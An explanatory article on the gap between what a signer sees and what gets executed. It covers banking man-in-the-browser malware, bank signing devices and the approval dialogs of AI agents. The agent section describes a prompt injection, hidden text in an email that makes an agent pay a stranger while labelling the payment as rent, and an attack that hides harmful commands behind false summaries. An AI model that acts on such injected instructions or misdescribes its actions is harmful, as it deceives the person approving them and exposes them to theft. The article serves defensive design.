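# What you see is what you sign: bank transfers, crypto wallets and the approval of AI agents' actions

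## Why a displayed text and an executed transaction can differ

What you see is what you sign (WYSIWYS) is the computer security requirement that the content shown to a signer match the content the signature covers. It matters wherever a person reads a display while a machine acts on data, as in online banking, cryptocurrency custody and, more recently, the approval dialogs of AI agents.

Suppose a tenant pays the rent from a laptop. The screen reads "€950 to my landlord", the tenant presses Approve, and the laptop sends the bank an order to pay €950 into a stranger's account. Malware inside a browser can do this without guessing a password or breaking any encryption. The laptop is the host, meaning the computer, phone or browser on which a person prepares a transaction and which an attacker may control.

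The approval can fail in three places. The screen may show the tenant false text, because whoever controls the host can make it display anything. The host may display the landlord's order accurately but pass the stranger's order to the signing chip, so that the tenant signs a different order from the one on the screen. The bank may also execute a different order from the one the tenant signed, if the proof of approval is valid for more than one order.

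### Signatures, codes and displays

A digital signature uses two keys. The signer keeps the private key, and everyone else may have the public one. Signing software usually starts by running the data through a hash function to compute a digest, a short fingerprint that changes if a single character of the data changes. The software then uses the private key to turn the digest into a signature, and anyone with the public key can check whether the signature matches the data. If a thief alters the account number after the tenant has signed, the check fails. A message authentication code works similarly, but with one secret key that both sides hold. Kiljan, Vranken and van Eekelen note in *User-friendly Manual Transfer of Authenticated Online Banking Transaction Data* that such a code cannot prove which side produced it, since both could have.

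Many approvals rely on something weaker, such as a one-time code or a passkey. A one-time code is a short number, valid once, that the customer receives or generates and types into the bank's page. A passkey is a key pair whose private half stays with the user's authenticator, such as a phone, and signs a challenge from a website. Both are good evidence that the right person or device is present. But neither an ordinary one-time code nor a passkey's signature over a random challenge is tied to the sum of €950. Malware can wait for the tenant to type the code, then use it to approve the stranger's order.

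The remedy is binding, which means tying an approval to exact data so that it is invalid for any other data. In one banking design that Kiljan and colleagues describe, the customer enters the payment details into a small separate device, which computes the approval code from them. If the order on the laptop differs, the code does not match it. Designers also add a number that never repeats, such as a counter or a time stamp, because otherwise an attacker could send the same valid order twice.

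Binding protects an order from approval onward, but it does not prevent a swap that happens earlier. The classic case is the smart card, a tamper-resistant chip that holds a private key and signs with it, so that the PC never has access to the key. Balfanz and Felten (1999), in *Hand-Held Computers Can Be Better Smart Cards*, pointed out that an attacker who controls the PC does not need the key. In their example, the owner writes an email to the president reading "I support you", but a malicious mail program sends the card the sentence "I conspired to kill you". The card signs that sentence, and the signature is mathematically valid and could stand up in court.

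The card's weakness is that it has no screen. In *Providing Authentication to Messages Signed with a Smart Card in Hostile Environments*, Stabell-Kulø, Arild and Myrvang (1999) concluded that the owner must trust the PC as much as the card, in which case the PC might as well do the signing. They then proposed a way to use the card without trusting the PC. An online server checks the signature and sends the signed message back through the PC, scrambled with a secret table of numbers that only the server and the user hold. The user repeats the scrambling by hand, one addition per character, and if the results agree, releases a secret number to accept the signature. Practised users needed 3 to 4 seconds per character. The paper's example, an instruction to pay someone $500, has 23 characters, so checking it would take more than a minute. Stabell-Kulø et al. remark that a hand-held computer with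 a small screen would solve the problem more simply.

Such a screen is called a trusted display because we assume, as part of the threat model (a statement of what the attacker can and cannot do), that the attacker cannot alter what it shows. That assumption may be wrong. Balfanz and Felten put their signing software on a PalmPilot, a 1990s pocket computer, and conceded that other programs on it might read the private key at the right moment, because the device did not protect one program's memory from another.

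A display only carries information to the person, who also has to answer. If the answer travels through the host, the host can forge it. A trusted path is a two-way channel between trusted code and the person in which an attacker can neither alter what the person sees nor answer for them. Langweg and Kristiansen (2006), in *Extending the Trusted Path in Client-Server Interaction*, wanted this channel to run from a server to the person at the keyboard, for uses including internet banking and online voting. On the PalmPilot, the owner answered by entering the PIN on the device itself. With an ordinary smart card, the PIN passes through the PC, where a malicious program can learn it and then use the card without the owner's knowledge.

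### Where the phrase comes from

The earliest paper to carry the full phrase "what you see is what you sign" seems to be Landrock and Pedersen's *WYSIWYS?* (1998), which has it in the title with a question mark. Cryptomathic's *What is WYSIWYS?* credits them with coining the term, but Landrock founded the company and Pedersen was its chief technology officer, so it has an interest in the matter. Weber's *See what you sign secure implementations of digital signatures* (1998) used almost the same words, and it is hard to settle who said it first. The problem is older than the phrase, since Stabell-Kulø and colleagues called it well known in 1999 and cited work on smart cards from 1993.

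*Digital Signatures and Electronic Documents* (Kain, Smith and Asokan, 2002) showed that a document alone can mislead its signer, without the untrustworthy machine that had been the early worry. A person who signs a file means to approve the page they see, but the signature covers the file. If the same file can produce two different pages, the signature is valid for both. Kain, Smith and Asokan built such files with ordinary office software. In one Word document, a date field made a witness's sentence begin "I did not have" before the 16th of the month and "I did have" from then on. The file's bytes appeared to stay the same, so the signature remained valid. An HTML email loaded part of its text as an image from a web server, so the sender could change the wording after someone had signed it.

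Kain and colleagues also described how an employee could profit by submitting an expense form that displays small sums when the approver opens it and large ones when the cashier does. The cashier checks the approver's signature, finds it valid, and pays. Several commercial signing products accepted these Word and Excel files. One, built into the office software, verified the signature when the document opened, before the content changed. Others resisted the attack. Adobe Acrobat's invisible signatures did very well because a user could easily compare the page before and after a change. The researchers say their findings stopped their university from deploying a flawed signing system.

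One response is to restrict what a person can sign. In *Robust WYSIWYS*, Josang and Alfayyadh (2008) argued that signing on a general-purpose computer is untrustworthy in principle, because it is extremely difficult to establish whether such a machine is intact. Their method works directly only on documents in plain ASCII characters, which are the basic letters, digits and punctuation marks. Richer formatting would first need a specially defined layout language. The restriction makes sense given the Word example, because plain text leaves little room for text that changes with the date.

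Lioy, Ramunno and colleagues, in *Motivations for a theoretical approach to WYSIWYS*, went further and called the slogan "intrinsically wrong". Nobody ever sees what they sign, because they sign bits and see one possible representation of those bits. Finding no agreed definition in the literature, they offered one. Let *F<sub>S</sub>* be the chain of steps that turns a document into a picture on the signer's machine, and *F<sub>V</sub>* the corresponding chain on the machine of whoever verifies the signature later. The requirement is that

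*F<sub>S</sub>*(doc) ≡ *F<sub>V</sub>*(doc),

where ≡ stands for "has the same meaning as", at any time after signing and on any computer. The two pictures need not be identical. An order that arrives by fax in poor quality is still the same order if the recipient can read all of it without ambiguity.

This definition suits contracts, which a second person reads. A bank's computer processes a payment, so the text the payer sees has to match the transfer the computer makes. When the tenant approves a payment to "my landlord", the account number the bank uses has to be the landlord's. Makers of hardware wallets, small devices that hold a cryptocurrency key and have their own screen, adopted the slogan for this kind of case. *Clear Signing*, a page by the wallet maker Ledger, gives it as the guiding principle.

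### Four conditions for an approval

*What You Approve Is What Executes* (Weng, 2026) turned the slogan into a definition for actions in general. The definition assumes a trusted mediator, a program that sits between whoever requests an action and the system that carries it out, and so observes the real action. An approval then has to satisfy four conditions.

1. Truthful rendering. The mediator computes the text that the person reads from the action itself, and never from a description by the party that requests it.
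2. All consequential facts shown. Weng's word for this is faithfulness. For software running on someone's computer the facts include where data goes over the network, whether the action reads passwords or keys, and whether it destroys anything irreversibly.
3. A trusted path. The text reaches the person, and the answer comes back, over a channel on which the requesting party can neither draw nor reply.
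4. Binding to execution. No other action can execute under the consent that the person gave for this one.

The opening example does not meet the first condition, because the laptop's software displayed the words "€950 to my landlord" without deriving them from the order that went to the bank.

Even with that problem fixed, a trusted program that reads the real order could display only "€950, rent". Those words are correct, but they omit a stranger's account number and an instruction to repeat the payment every month. An approval can therefore fail on the second condition even when everything displayed is true.

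Suppose next that the trusted program composes a complete and correct text but shows it in a window on the laptop. The malware can cover that window with its own, so that the tenant never reads the text, or press Approve itself, so that the tenant never answers. In both cases the third condition is not met, even though the text is correct.

In the last case, the tenant reads the landlord's correct account number on a screen nobody has tampered with, and approves. A second later, the laptop submits a different order with the same approval. Security engineers call this gap TOCTOU, for "time of check to time of use". To close it, Weng's mediator stores a digest of the approved action and rejects any action whose digest differs.

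Weng acknowledges that the second condition is an ideal, because no program can decode every possible action. As a fallback, when the program cannot classify an action, it labels the action uninspectable or high-risk, so that the action is never shown with a harmless description. The definition also does not require that the person understand what is displayed. A tenant who has forgotten the landlord's account number can approve a payment to the wrong account even if the display is truthful, complete and bound.

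### An agent that describes its own action

An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses steps towards a goal and carries them out through other software. It does this with tool calls, which are structured requests containing the name of a tool and its arguments. A call to a payment tool, for instance, might contain an amount of 950, a currency and an account number. Many agents that write and run code show the user a confirmation dialog before consequential calls and wait for a response.

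The agent usually writes the text in that dialog. This makes it a narrated prompt, and its weakness becomes serious with prompt injection, in which instructions are hidden in material the agent reads. Suppose the tenant asks an agent to pay the rent according to the latest email from the landlord. A stranger has sent an email stating, in white text on a white background, that the landlord's account has changed and that the agent should describe the payment as the usual rent. The model processes the tenant's request and the stranger's sentence as the same kind of text and may follow both. If it does, it prepares a tool call with the stranger's account number and writes "€950 to my landlord" in the dialog.

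The agent is now in the position of the compromised laptop, because it both prepares the order and writes the description the tenant uses to judge it. Weng therefore assumes an attacker who controls everything the agent produces, including its summaries and the characters it writes to the screen. Researchers at the security company Checkmarx had demonstrated the problem in 2025 with an attack called Lies-in-the-Loop, which makes a harmful command look safe in the dialog with a false summary or with harmless filler that pushes the command out of view. According to Weng, the vendors who received the report classed it as outside their threat models. A model can also produce the same mismatch without malice, by getting its summary wrong.

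One of the two differences Weng names from the older cases is that the component that writes the description is itself the adversary. That was also true of the mail program in the smart card example, so the problem seems less new than Weng suggests. The remedy, however, has to go in a different place. A manufacturer can put a screen on the device that holds the key, but an agent comes with no such device, so someone has to place a trusted program outside the agent, at the point where the tool call leaves.

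The other difference is that the gap between the raw action and its meaning is wider with agents. A bank transfer has a handful of fields, whereas an agent may run a command that unpacks another command from an encoded string, and an attacker can choose the encoding. Weng holds that classical WYSIWYS has no such gap, because the signed object already is the meaningful one. That is too strong. The meaning of the signed Word file with the date field depended on the software that opened it, and Ledger describes wallet users who face a screen full of unreadable transaction data.

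The person approving a payment may also not know what the display should read. The tenant at the laptop knows because they typed the order. But the tenant who asked an agent to "pay the rent" may never have looked up the landlord's account number, and so would have nothing to compare the display with, even if it showed the transaction correctly.

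## How malware in the browser changes a bank transfer

The altered rent payment is an example of a man-in-the-browser attack, in which malware in the customer's browser changes both the order sent to the bank and the pages the customer sees. *Concepts against Man-in-the-Browser Attacks* (Gühring, 2006) set out the attack in 18 steps while it was still new. Such malware already worked in Firefox, Internet Explorer and Opera, and Gühring thought anyone with web design experience could write it.

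### The attack in order

The malware first installs an extension, an add-on program that the browser loads whenever it starts. The extension can read and change the pages the browser displays. It checks the address of each page against a list of bank sites until it finds a transfer form on one of them.

The tenant opens the bank's real website, logs in, enters €950 and the landlord's account number, and presses Submit. The extension then saves a copy of everything in the form. It replaces the landlord's account number with a stranger's, can also raise the amount, and lets the browser send the form. The bank receives an ordinary order from a correctly logged-in customer and cannot tell that the values have changed.

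Many banks ask the customer to confirm before they pay. *Threat Landscape 2008* (Ramzan, 2008) illustrates this stage with Silentbanker, malware that the security company Symantec had analysed. The bank returns a confirmation page showing the stranger's account, and the malware puts the original account back before the page appears. The bank also sends a password to the customer's mobile phone. The customer sees the expected payment, types the password, and so approves the payment to the stranger.

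The malware still has to hide the result. When the bank's receipt arrives, Gühring's extension replaces the altered details with the ones it stored. URLZone, banking malware from 2009, also rewrote the account statement. Dark Reading's *New Trojan Evades Banks' Anti-Fraud Systems* describes a case in which thieves took €8,576 while the victim's screen showed a transfer of €53.94. The bank's own records were correct, so the victim could have discovered the theft by logging in from an uninfected computer. *Malware that Forges Bank Statements*, a 2009 post on cryptographer Bruce Schneier's blog, Schneier on Security, concluded that banks cannot rely on the customer to detect fraud.

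The usual signs of safety don't reveal this attack. Encryption stops anyone on the network between the browser and the bank from reading or altering the order, but the malware changes the form before the browser encrypts it and the reply after the browser decrypts it. Checking the web address protects against phishing, where a fake site imitates the bank, but the tenant is on the real site. The login is genuine too, and the malware doesn't need to impersonate the tenant because it works inside the session the tenant has opened.

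### What each code depends on

The banks' early defences were mostly better ways of checking who was using the computer. The simplest check is a password, which is the same for every transfer and so contains no information about any particular one. Malware can also copy the password, letting thieves log in later from their own computer.

Some banks added a printed list of transaction numbers, each valid once, so that a thief who has only the password can no longer pay anyone. But the bank prints the list long before the tenant decides to pay the rent, so no number on it can depend on the amount or the payee. In an improved version, the bank asks for the number at a particular position, say the 37th. A few stolen numbers are then less useful, because the thief cannot choose which one the bank will request. Malware can still change the transfer, however. The bank asks for the 37th number to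 approve the payment to the stranger, the malware displays that request next to the landlord's details, and the tenant types the number in.

A small token generates a time-based code by combining a secret with the current time, and the code expires soon afterwards. A thief who steals a code therefore can't use it the next day. In a man-in-the-browser attack, however, the tenant enters a fresh code while it is still valid, so its expiry doesn't protect them. Thieves can also use a stolen code before it expires. According to Krebs on Security (2025), a gang known as Jabber Zeus used malware that sent it an instant message each time a new victim entered a one-time code at a bank's website.

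Gühring's list of methods that fail also includes fingerprints and other biometrics, and smart cards, even in a reader with its own small display. The display doesn't help if the bank uses the card only to check who is logging in, because the display never shows the payment.

If the bank sends a code by text message to the tenant's phone, an attacker who controls only the laptop cannot read or change the message. How much this helps depends on what the message contains. Suppose it reads only "Your code is 482913". The bank's server may accept that code for only one pending order, but that order is already for a payment to the stranger, and the tenant cannot tell this from the message.

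The other kind of message repeats the amount and the payee's account number next to the code. Gühring reports that several European banks were developing this method. The bank composes the message from the order it received, so the tenant would see the stranger's account number on the phone and the landlord's on the laptop, and could refuse to enter the code. This is the only early defence that gives the customer a chance to notice the change. But a text message holds only 160 characters, too few to list the payments when a business approves many together, and the phone may store confidential payment details indefinitely.

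The difference also matters outside banking. A reader of Schneier's blog described a fraud in Taiwan, where telephone companies let customers charge purchases to their phone bill by entering a code from a text message. Fraudsters told people they had won something and needed to enter the next code to claim it. Because the message contained only a code, the victims did not see that they were buying game credit for someone else. The reader suggested putting the purchase details in the message.

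### Checks on the same computer

A second device adds expense and effort, so vendors and banks also looked for a way to show the true payment on the infected computer. Higgins (2007), in *Killing That 'Man in the Browser'*, reported on a TriCipher product that ran on the same screen as the browser but had its own encrypted connection. If a customer entered $200 and malware changed it to $500, the separate program would show the discrepancy before the customer confirmed. That would work against malware confined to the browser, but malware that controls the whole computer can alter the separate window too.

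Gühring found similar weaknesses in other proposals. Banks could send the payment details as a picture, on the theory that text in a picture is hard to edit, but an attacker can replace the whole picture. A bank's server could also delay part of a page and, if the text changes within five seconds, show a warning that the browser has been taken over. This catches only malware that waits for the page to finish loading. Starting the computer from a read-only disc with a clean operating system is much stronger protection, but each restart takes one to three minutes, and at the time such discs usually lacked printer drivers.

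### Silentbanker, Zeus and URLZone

Silentbanker, which attracted attention in January 2008, targeted 400 banks in many countries, but Virus Bulletin (2008) reported that it could reroute transfers only at certain ones and mostly used fake login pages. According to the Symantec analysis quoted in Financial Cryptography's *Trojan with Everything, To Go!* (2008), this was because the malware stole usernames and passwords wherever those were enough to move money. Symantec's analysts inferred the payee swap from the program's code and could not reproduce such a transaction exactly in their laboratory. They gave no figure for losses. Silentbanker is therefore good evidence that criminals had built the attack, but weaker evidence of how much they stole with it.

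In October 2010, the FBI said that one gang had used Zeus, a common family of banking malware, to steal $70 million from hundreds of small and mid-sized American businesses over 18 months, according to Krebs on Security's *Ukraine Detains 5 Individuals Tied to $70 Million in eBanking Heists* (2010). The gang had tried to steal $220 million in all. The businesses usually bore the loss themselves. The investigation began in May 2009, when FBI agents in Omaha learned of batch payments to 46 bank accounts.

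Much of the $70 million may have left through transfers that the thieves entered themselves with stolen credentials, so the whole sum should not be counted as altered transfers. eWeek's *Ukraine Police Arrest 5 over $70M Zeus Trojan Bank Scheme* describes the gang's version of Zeus as a tool for capturing account numbers, passwords and other login data. Krebs on Security calls the gang a pioneer of man-in-the-browser attacks, but uses the term for malware that intercepts whatever a victim types into a web form, which is broader than changing a payment the customer is making.

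URLZone is a clearer case of deception on the screen, though the sums were smaller. The security company Finjan, which discovered it, said in *Cybercriminals use Trojans and Money Mules to Loot Online Bank Accounts* (2009) that the gang stole €300,000 in 22 days. Zetter (2009), in *New Malware Re-Writes Online Bank Statements to Cover Fraud*, gave the same total and placed the thefts in August, among customers of leading German banks. Dark Reading instead reported about €200,000 a day, which is probably a mistake, because the same article projects the gang's yearly income at $7.3 million. At 2009 exchange rates, that roughly matches €300,000 in 22 days, or about €5 million a year, whereas €200,000 a day would come to €73 million a year.

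By 2014 the technique was routine. *Protecting financial institutions from man-in-the-browser attacks* (2014) cited reports of attacks on more than 1,400 financial institutions, and found that almost all banking malware of the time inserted its own code into the bank's pages. That code could steal passwords as well as change transfers, so the count includes both kinds of attack.

### When the malware reaches the phone

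Text messages add security because an attacker must control two devices. The attackers in the Eurograbber campaign, which the security companies Check Point and Versafe described in December 2012, controlled both.

*Boosting usability for Protecting Online Banking Applications Against APTs* (Alhanahnah and Chadwick, 2016) explains how Zeus worked. Zeus first infected the customer's PC. When the customer visited the bank's site, the altered page asked for details of their mobile phone, supposedly to install security software on it, but the software was more malware. Zeus then inserted its own transfer into the banking session. When the bank sent a code to the phone, the malware there intercepted it and relayed it to Zeus, which used it to approve the transfer.

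Silentbanker needed the customer to type in the phone password. Eurograbber's victims did not have to approve anything, because the attackers read and answered the bank's messages themselves. Alhanahnah and Chadwick state that these messages included the transaction details. If so, the details were accurate but did not protect the customers, because the messages went to the malware instead of to someone who could have rejected the transfer.

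Jacob's *Check Point and Versafe Uncover New Eurograbber Attack* (2012) reports that the thieves took more than €36 million from over 30,000 customers of more than 30 banks. That is about €1,200 per customer, and Check Point puts individual transfers at between €500 and €250,000. These numbers come from companies that sell protection against such attacks, so an independent count would be useful. Trend Micro's *Finding Holes* (2014) described a later campaign, named Emmental, that also got around text-message codes in several countries.

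Eurograbber's attackers had to infect both a PC and a phone, but if a customer does all their banking on a phone, attackers need to infect only that phone. A reader of Schneier's blog complained in 2012 that text-message codes had been convenient and fairly safe until people began to log in to their bank from the same phone that received the codes. An app that approves payments has the same weakness if it runs on the phone where the customer enters them. On Android, malware can use the accessibility service, a feature for people with disabilities that lets one app read another's screen and press its buttons. With that permission, the malware can both fill in a transfer and confirm it.

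Alhanahnah and Chadwick concluded that the device which confirms a payment should not be able to download software, which rules out mobile phones. They also recognised that banks might hesitate to buy a separate device because of its price. If only a tenth of the eurozone's 332 million people banked online, Eurograbber cost about €1 per online customer, while the cheap card reader that many German banks used cost €15.

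### Authenticating the transaction

In 2005, Schneier predicted that attackers would get around two-factor authentication (a password combined with something like a code or token) by interfering with transactions in real time. In *The Failure of Two-Factor Authentication* (Schneier on Security, 2012), he cited a BBC report of such attacks and concluded: "The solution is to authenticate the transaction, not the person." One reader objected that he had never explained what this meant, and it can mean two different things.

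The bank can look for suspicious payments, as credit card companies do. This doesn't rely on the customer's display, but attackers can adapt to it. To avoid triggering the bank's alarms, URLZone's operators set a minimum and maximum for each theft based on the victim's balance, and used each money mule (a person who forwards stolen funds) at most twice. Some banks telephoned customers about unusual payments. Alhanahnah and Chadwick describe fraudsters who got around this by tricking customers into revealing their telephone account details, then having the telephone company redirect the bank's calls to the fraudsters' own call centre.

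A bank can instead bind the customer's approval to the particular amount and payee. The EU later added a rule of this kind to its payment law, and some banks issued separate devices for the purpose. This works against a man-in-the-browser attack only if a trusted display shows the details of the order the bank actually received and the customer reads them.

The customer also has to know what the numbers mean. DShield's *Strong (two factor) authentication and still vulnerable?* reported that many people typing digits into a bank token did not realise they were entering account numbers and amounts. They thought they were just copying a string and typing the result back into the website. The code depended on those digits being right, but these customers had no reason to check them. A display that reads "Pay €950 to account 51234829348" at least shows them what to compare.

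In the BBC case, which is harder to prevent, the malware offered customers training in an "upgraded security system" after they logged in to the real site, and money then left their accounts. Schneier presented this as a failure to authenticate the transaction, but a reader pointed out that Barclays customers already had to enter the amount and a payee reference number into a separate card reader. On that account, the approvals were tied to the fraudulent transfers, and customers entered the details themselves because they thought it was an exercise. A clear warning on the card reader that real money is about to leave the account would help, but the malware could still display a message on the laptop telling customers to ignore it as part of the training.

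An attack can also begin before the customer opens the bank's website. Malware, or someone with access to a mail server, changes the account number in an emailed bill. If a tenant copies the altered number from a landlord's email, the laptop, the text message and the bank's order will all show the altered number. The tenant can catch the fraud only by comparing that number with a copy the attacker could not edit, such as the one in a paper lease.

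## Bank devices that display the transaction before signing it

In the 2000s, European banks began giving customers small devices with their own screen and keypad, so that malware on a laptop no longer controlled everything the customer saw. When the tenant pays the rent with such a device, either the tenant types in the payment details or the bank sends the device the order it has received. The device displays the landlord's account number and the €950, the tenant confirms, and the device computes a code from those details with a secret key that the bank also holds. The tenant types the code into the bank's page, and the bank repeats the calculation on the order it is about to execute.

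If the tenant typed the details into the device, the code will not match an order that malware has altered. If the bank sent the details, the device shows the stranger's account number, and the tenant can refuse to sign.

All of this assumes that the attacker never tampers with the device. *Designed to Fail* (Blom, de Koning Gans et al., 2012) points out that readers for home use are barely tamper-resistant, because better ones would cost far too much. Dutch criminals obtained PINs by tampering with readers that customers could use inside bank branches.

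### What the customer sees and does

British banks gave away a plain card reader that used the Chip Authentication Programme (CAP), MasterCard's scheme for computing codes with an ordinary bank card. The standard was secret, so Drimer, Murdoch and Anderson reconstructed it in *Optimised to Fail* (2009), partly by recording the traffic between card and reader. They describe CAP as a cheap substitute for proper signing devices with trustworthy displays, which typically cost $100 or more.

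The customer inserts the card, types the PIN and chooses one of three modes. "Identify" mode produces a one-time code with no further input. In "respond" mode the customer types in a challenge, a number displayed on the bank's web page. In "sign" mode they type the payee's account number and the amount. The card computes a message authentication code over whatever the customer typed and its transaction counter, and the reader shortens the result to a number the customer can copy.

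Barclays used sign mode for payments, so a code was valid only for that payee and amount. The code did not depend on a fresh value from the bank, so Barclays could not tell when the customer had generated it. NatWest used respond mode with an eight-digit challenge, made up of four random digits followed by the last four digits of the payee's account number, so the code did not depend on the amount.

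German banks call a one-time code a TAN, short for transaction number. Their chipTAN procedure dates from 2006, according to *An easy target for hackers* (2015), a release by the University of Erlangen-Nuremberg (FAU). At first the customer typed the payee and the amount into both the laptop and the device. Reiner SCT, which makes such devices, advertised "no double entry" for the next version.

That version, chipTAN comfort, reads a flicker code from the bank's web page, made up of five bars that switch between black and white. The customer holds the device, which is about the size of a pocket calculator, against the screen, where five light sensors on its back read the bars. The device then displays the account number and the amount. The customer confirms each one and copies the resulting code into the web page. Blom and colleagues mention that a similar German system has the advantage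 of sending light only from the PC to the reader, which prevents two-way communication between malware and the device.

The Cambridge company Cronto replaced the flickering bars with a still picture made of coloured dots. The customer scans it with a phone app or a separate device, reads a message from the bank, and types a six-digit code into the browser. The message can be more than 100 characters long, according to the University of Cambridge's *New system to combat online banking fraud* (2013), which gives the bank room to point out anything unusual about the payment. Malware can access the picture but cannot change the data inside it. Murdoch, one of the researchers who had reverse-engineered CAP, was the security architect and worked on the protocol with Commerzbank, one of the German banks that offer this kind of scanning under the name photoTAN.

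In the most recent variant, the customer confirms the transaction on an ordinary phone, often without having to copy a code. Star Finanz's *S-pushTAN für iPhone und iPad 4+*, the app store page for the German savings banks' approval app, describes how the app displays the details of an order and the customer approves it with a swipe.

These displays also differ in what the customer can conclude from them. Blom and colleagues call a display trusted in the narrow sense if whatever it shows is part of what the card signs, and in the broad sense if the customer also knows that the bank wrote the text. Narrow trust is enough to establish what the customer agreed to, but an attacker can use the screen for phishing if the text could have come from anyone. Cronto's protected picture is meant to be trusted in the broad sense. So is the display on IBM's ZTIC, a small USB device that sets up its own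 encrypted connection to the bank, though it has to store keys and is more complex.

### Eight digits without a meaning

An eight-digit challenge has little room for a message. Blom and colleagues write that the digits are often random and the customer has no real idea what they are authorising.

Malware can therefore use the same trick as with the printed lists. It orders a payment to the stranger and displays the bank's challenge, say 40718826, below the words "€950 to my landlord". The tenant types the challenge into the reader, whose screen shows only that number, and copies back a response that approves the payment to the stranger.

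The reader displays the digits correctly but omits the payee and the sum, so the approval fails the condition that the person see all consequential facts. The browser supplies its own description instead, and because that is the only one the tenant reads, the approval also fails the condition of truthful rendering.

When the amount is large or the payee is new, some banks ask for additional challenges, such as the amount or the last eight digits of the payee's account number. These help only if the customer recognises them, and a compromised browser can present the last eight digits of the thief's account number as another random number. The customer then types them in and gets a code that is valid for the thief's transfer. NatWest's four digits have the same weakness, because the page can describe all eight digits as random.

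The fraudsters who offered Barclays customers "training" exploited this gap, and so did the Tatanga malware. Schneier (2012), in *Man-in-the-Middle Bank Fraud Attack*, quotes a description of how Tatanga chose the account from which it could steal the most, started a transfer, and then displayed a notice that the bank was carrying out a chipTAN test, for which the customer only had to generate a code and enter it. A chipTAN device would normally show the payee and the amount, so Tatanga depended on customers believing the web page over the device.

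Drimer and colleagues blame CAP's weaknesses on excessive optimisation. They argue that a protocol becomes fragile when its designers save effort by leaving out context that looks unimportant. In CAP, the same few input fields are used for a random challenge at one bank and an account number at another. Customers who meet different rules at different banks are easier to mislead.

### A confirmation the computer could supply

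If a cable connects the reader to the computer, the user doesn't have to type in challenges, so they can be longer. The Dutch bank ABN AMRO, which had 6.8 million customers, issued a reader, the e.dentifier2, that worked with or without a USB cable. Its screen held 68 characters. The manufacturer advertised it as "the most secure sign-what-you-see end-user device ever seen".

Blom and colleagues recorded the traffic on the cable and found that an approval ran as follows.

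1. The customer types the PIN on the reader, and the bank card checks it.
2. The computer sends the reader a text to display and a random number.
3. The reader displays the text, and the customer presses OK.
4. The reader reports to the computer that the customer has pressed OK.
5. The computer sends the reader a command to sign, and the card computes a code that depends on both the text and the number.

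The command to sign should have come from the reader's own OK button. Because it came from the computer instead, malware could send it right after step 2, without anyone pressing OK. The reader then produced a valid code. The command also cleared the screen, so the customer saw the payment details for less than a second. The customer still had to enter the PIN, but did so before the reader displayed any payment. The researchers carried out the attack in a real banking session, and ABN AMRO confirmed it from its own logs.

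The code was bound to the displayed text, and the researchers tried and failed to separate the two. But the design lacked a trusted path, so the attacker could answer in the customer's place.

The researchers were at first baffled by this design. Their best guess is that the flaw comes from the way the reader handles long messages. When the payment details need more than 68 characters, the computer sends them in several pieces, and the customer presses OK after each. OK can therefore mean either "show me more" or "go ahead and sign", and because the reader cannot distinguish the two, the computer controls which one happens. The design in the same company's patent application for a similar reader does not have the flaw. Testers could have found the problem by trying every kind of message in every internal state, since the reader had few of either.

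New software on the computer could not fix this. The supplier developed an improved reader, which ABN AMRO planned to distribute during 2012, but millions of the old readers were already in use.

Even with a working OK button, the reader would not have revealed a changed payee, a gap that Blom and colleagues do not dwell on. For payments, it displayed only the number of transfers and the total sum. In one recorded session the text was "1 transaction(s) EUR 123,00". If malware had replaced the landlord's account with the stranger's and left the amount alone, the display would have been the same. ABN AMRO did at least show some payment details on the reader's screen. The Swedish banks Handelsbanken and SEB also issued USB readers with displays, but their customers had to check payments on the computer.

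### A count and a total

The same omission could occur with chipTAN when German customers made a collective transfer, which combines several payments into one order with one code. *Man-in-the-Middle-Angriffe auf das chipTAN comfort-Verfahren im Online-Banking* (2009), by the security testing company RedTeam Pentesting, reports that the device displayed the total and the number of payments for such an order. EU payment law later included a rule for these batches.

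If a business pays ten suppliers in one order, malware can replace all ten account numbers with the thief's and keep the amounts. The device shows only the total and the number of payments, which stay the same, so the customer has no way to notice. The display is truthful, the code is bound to the order and nobody else presses the button. The approval fails only because the screen omits the payees and so doesn't show every consequential fact.

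This could also affect people who had never made a collective transfer. When the tenant enters a single payment of €950 to the landlord, the malware creates a collective order in the background, containing one payment of €950 to the thief. It shows the tenant the flicker code for that order and changes the web page's instructions to say that the tenant should check the amount and the number of transfers. The device displays €950 and a count of one, as the tenant now expects. Customers who remembered that the device usually shows an account number might become suspicious, but RedTeam Pentesting thought that even they would find the attack hard to spot.

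A third weakness concerned IBANs, the international account numbers of up to 34 characters. The device displayed only the third, fourth and last four characters. Malware could again change the instructions and direct the customer to other positions in the landlord's IBAN, where the six displayed characters of the thief's IBAN occurred. RedTeam Pentesting considered it very likely that the landlord's IBAN would contain these characters. For German IBANs, which have 20 digits, the chance of this is only about even for any one pair of accounts if the digits are random, but a thief with several accounts could choose one that fits.

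The company needed a few days to write a program that carried out one of these attacks automatically. RedTeam Pentesting's press release (2009) reports that the program redirected a transfer in a demonstration. No real thefts of this kind were known, and the company thought them unlikely while few people used chipTAN. It had reason to expect them later, because it had demonstrated an attack on the numbered TAN lists in 2005, and by 2008 at the latest criminals were using that attack against bank customers.

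RedTeam Pentesting still preferred chipTAN to the lists, because none of its attacks could change the amount unnoticed. It advised banks to teach customers exactly what the device should display for each kind of transfer, which would help against two of the three attacks. Only a fuller display would help against the third, which replaces the payees in a real collective transfer.

### Entering the payment on the device

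In each of these designs except CAP's sign mode and the first chipTAN, the customer enters the payment on the laptop and later compares it with a second screen. This comparison is unreliable because people often overlook a changed account number. Kiljan and colleagues propose removing the comparison with a scheme they call "what you enter is what you sign". The customer enters the payee and the amount only once, on the trusted device, which passes them to the laptop in a form the laptop cannot alter without the bank noticing.

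In Kiljan and colleagues' first version, the device sent the data to the computer by USB or Bluetooth, as if it were a keyboard. They dropped this because plugs differ and Bluetooth needs pairing and drains the battery. A connection would also have given malware another way to reach the device. In the revised version, the device displays a short text, the message code, which the customer types into the computer. This code contains the order itself, whereas an ordinary one-time code only confirms an order that the bank already has.

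The difficulty is to keep it short. The case study works through a transfer between two Dutch accounts. A Dutch account number has nine digits, which fit into 30 bits, and the bank can reconstruct the rest of the IBAN. An amount below €1 million, counted in cents, fits into 27 bits. Together they make a message *m* of 57 bits. The device then computes a message authentication code,

MAC = *H*(*k* | *n* | *m*),

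where *H* is the hash function SHA-3, *k* is a secret key shared with the bank, *n* is a counter that prevents reuse, and the vertical bars join the three pieces of data together. The MAC has 23 bits, which brings the total to 80. Sixteen characters of five bits each hold exactly that, and in the worked example a payment of €123,456.78 becomes "swpy-58n6-gnuz-q3gq".

If malware changes the account number, the MAC no longer matches and the bank rejects the order. The same check catches typing errors. The MAC's 23 bits allow about 8.4 million values, which is few by cryptographic standards, but only the bank can test a guess. If it blocks the account after ten wrong attempts, a forger who uses all ten has about a 1 in 840,000 chance of success.

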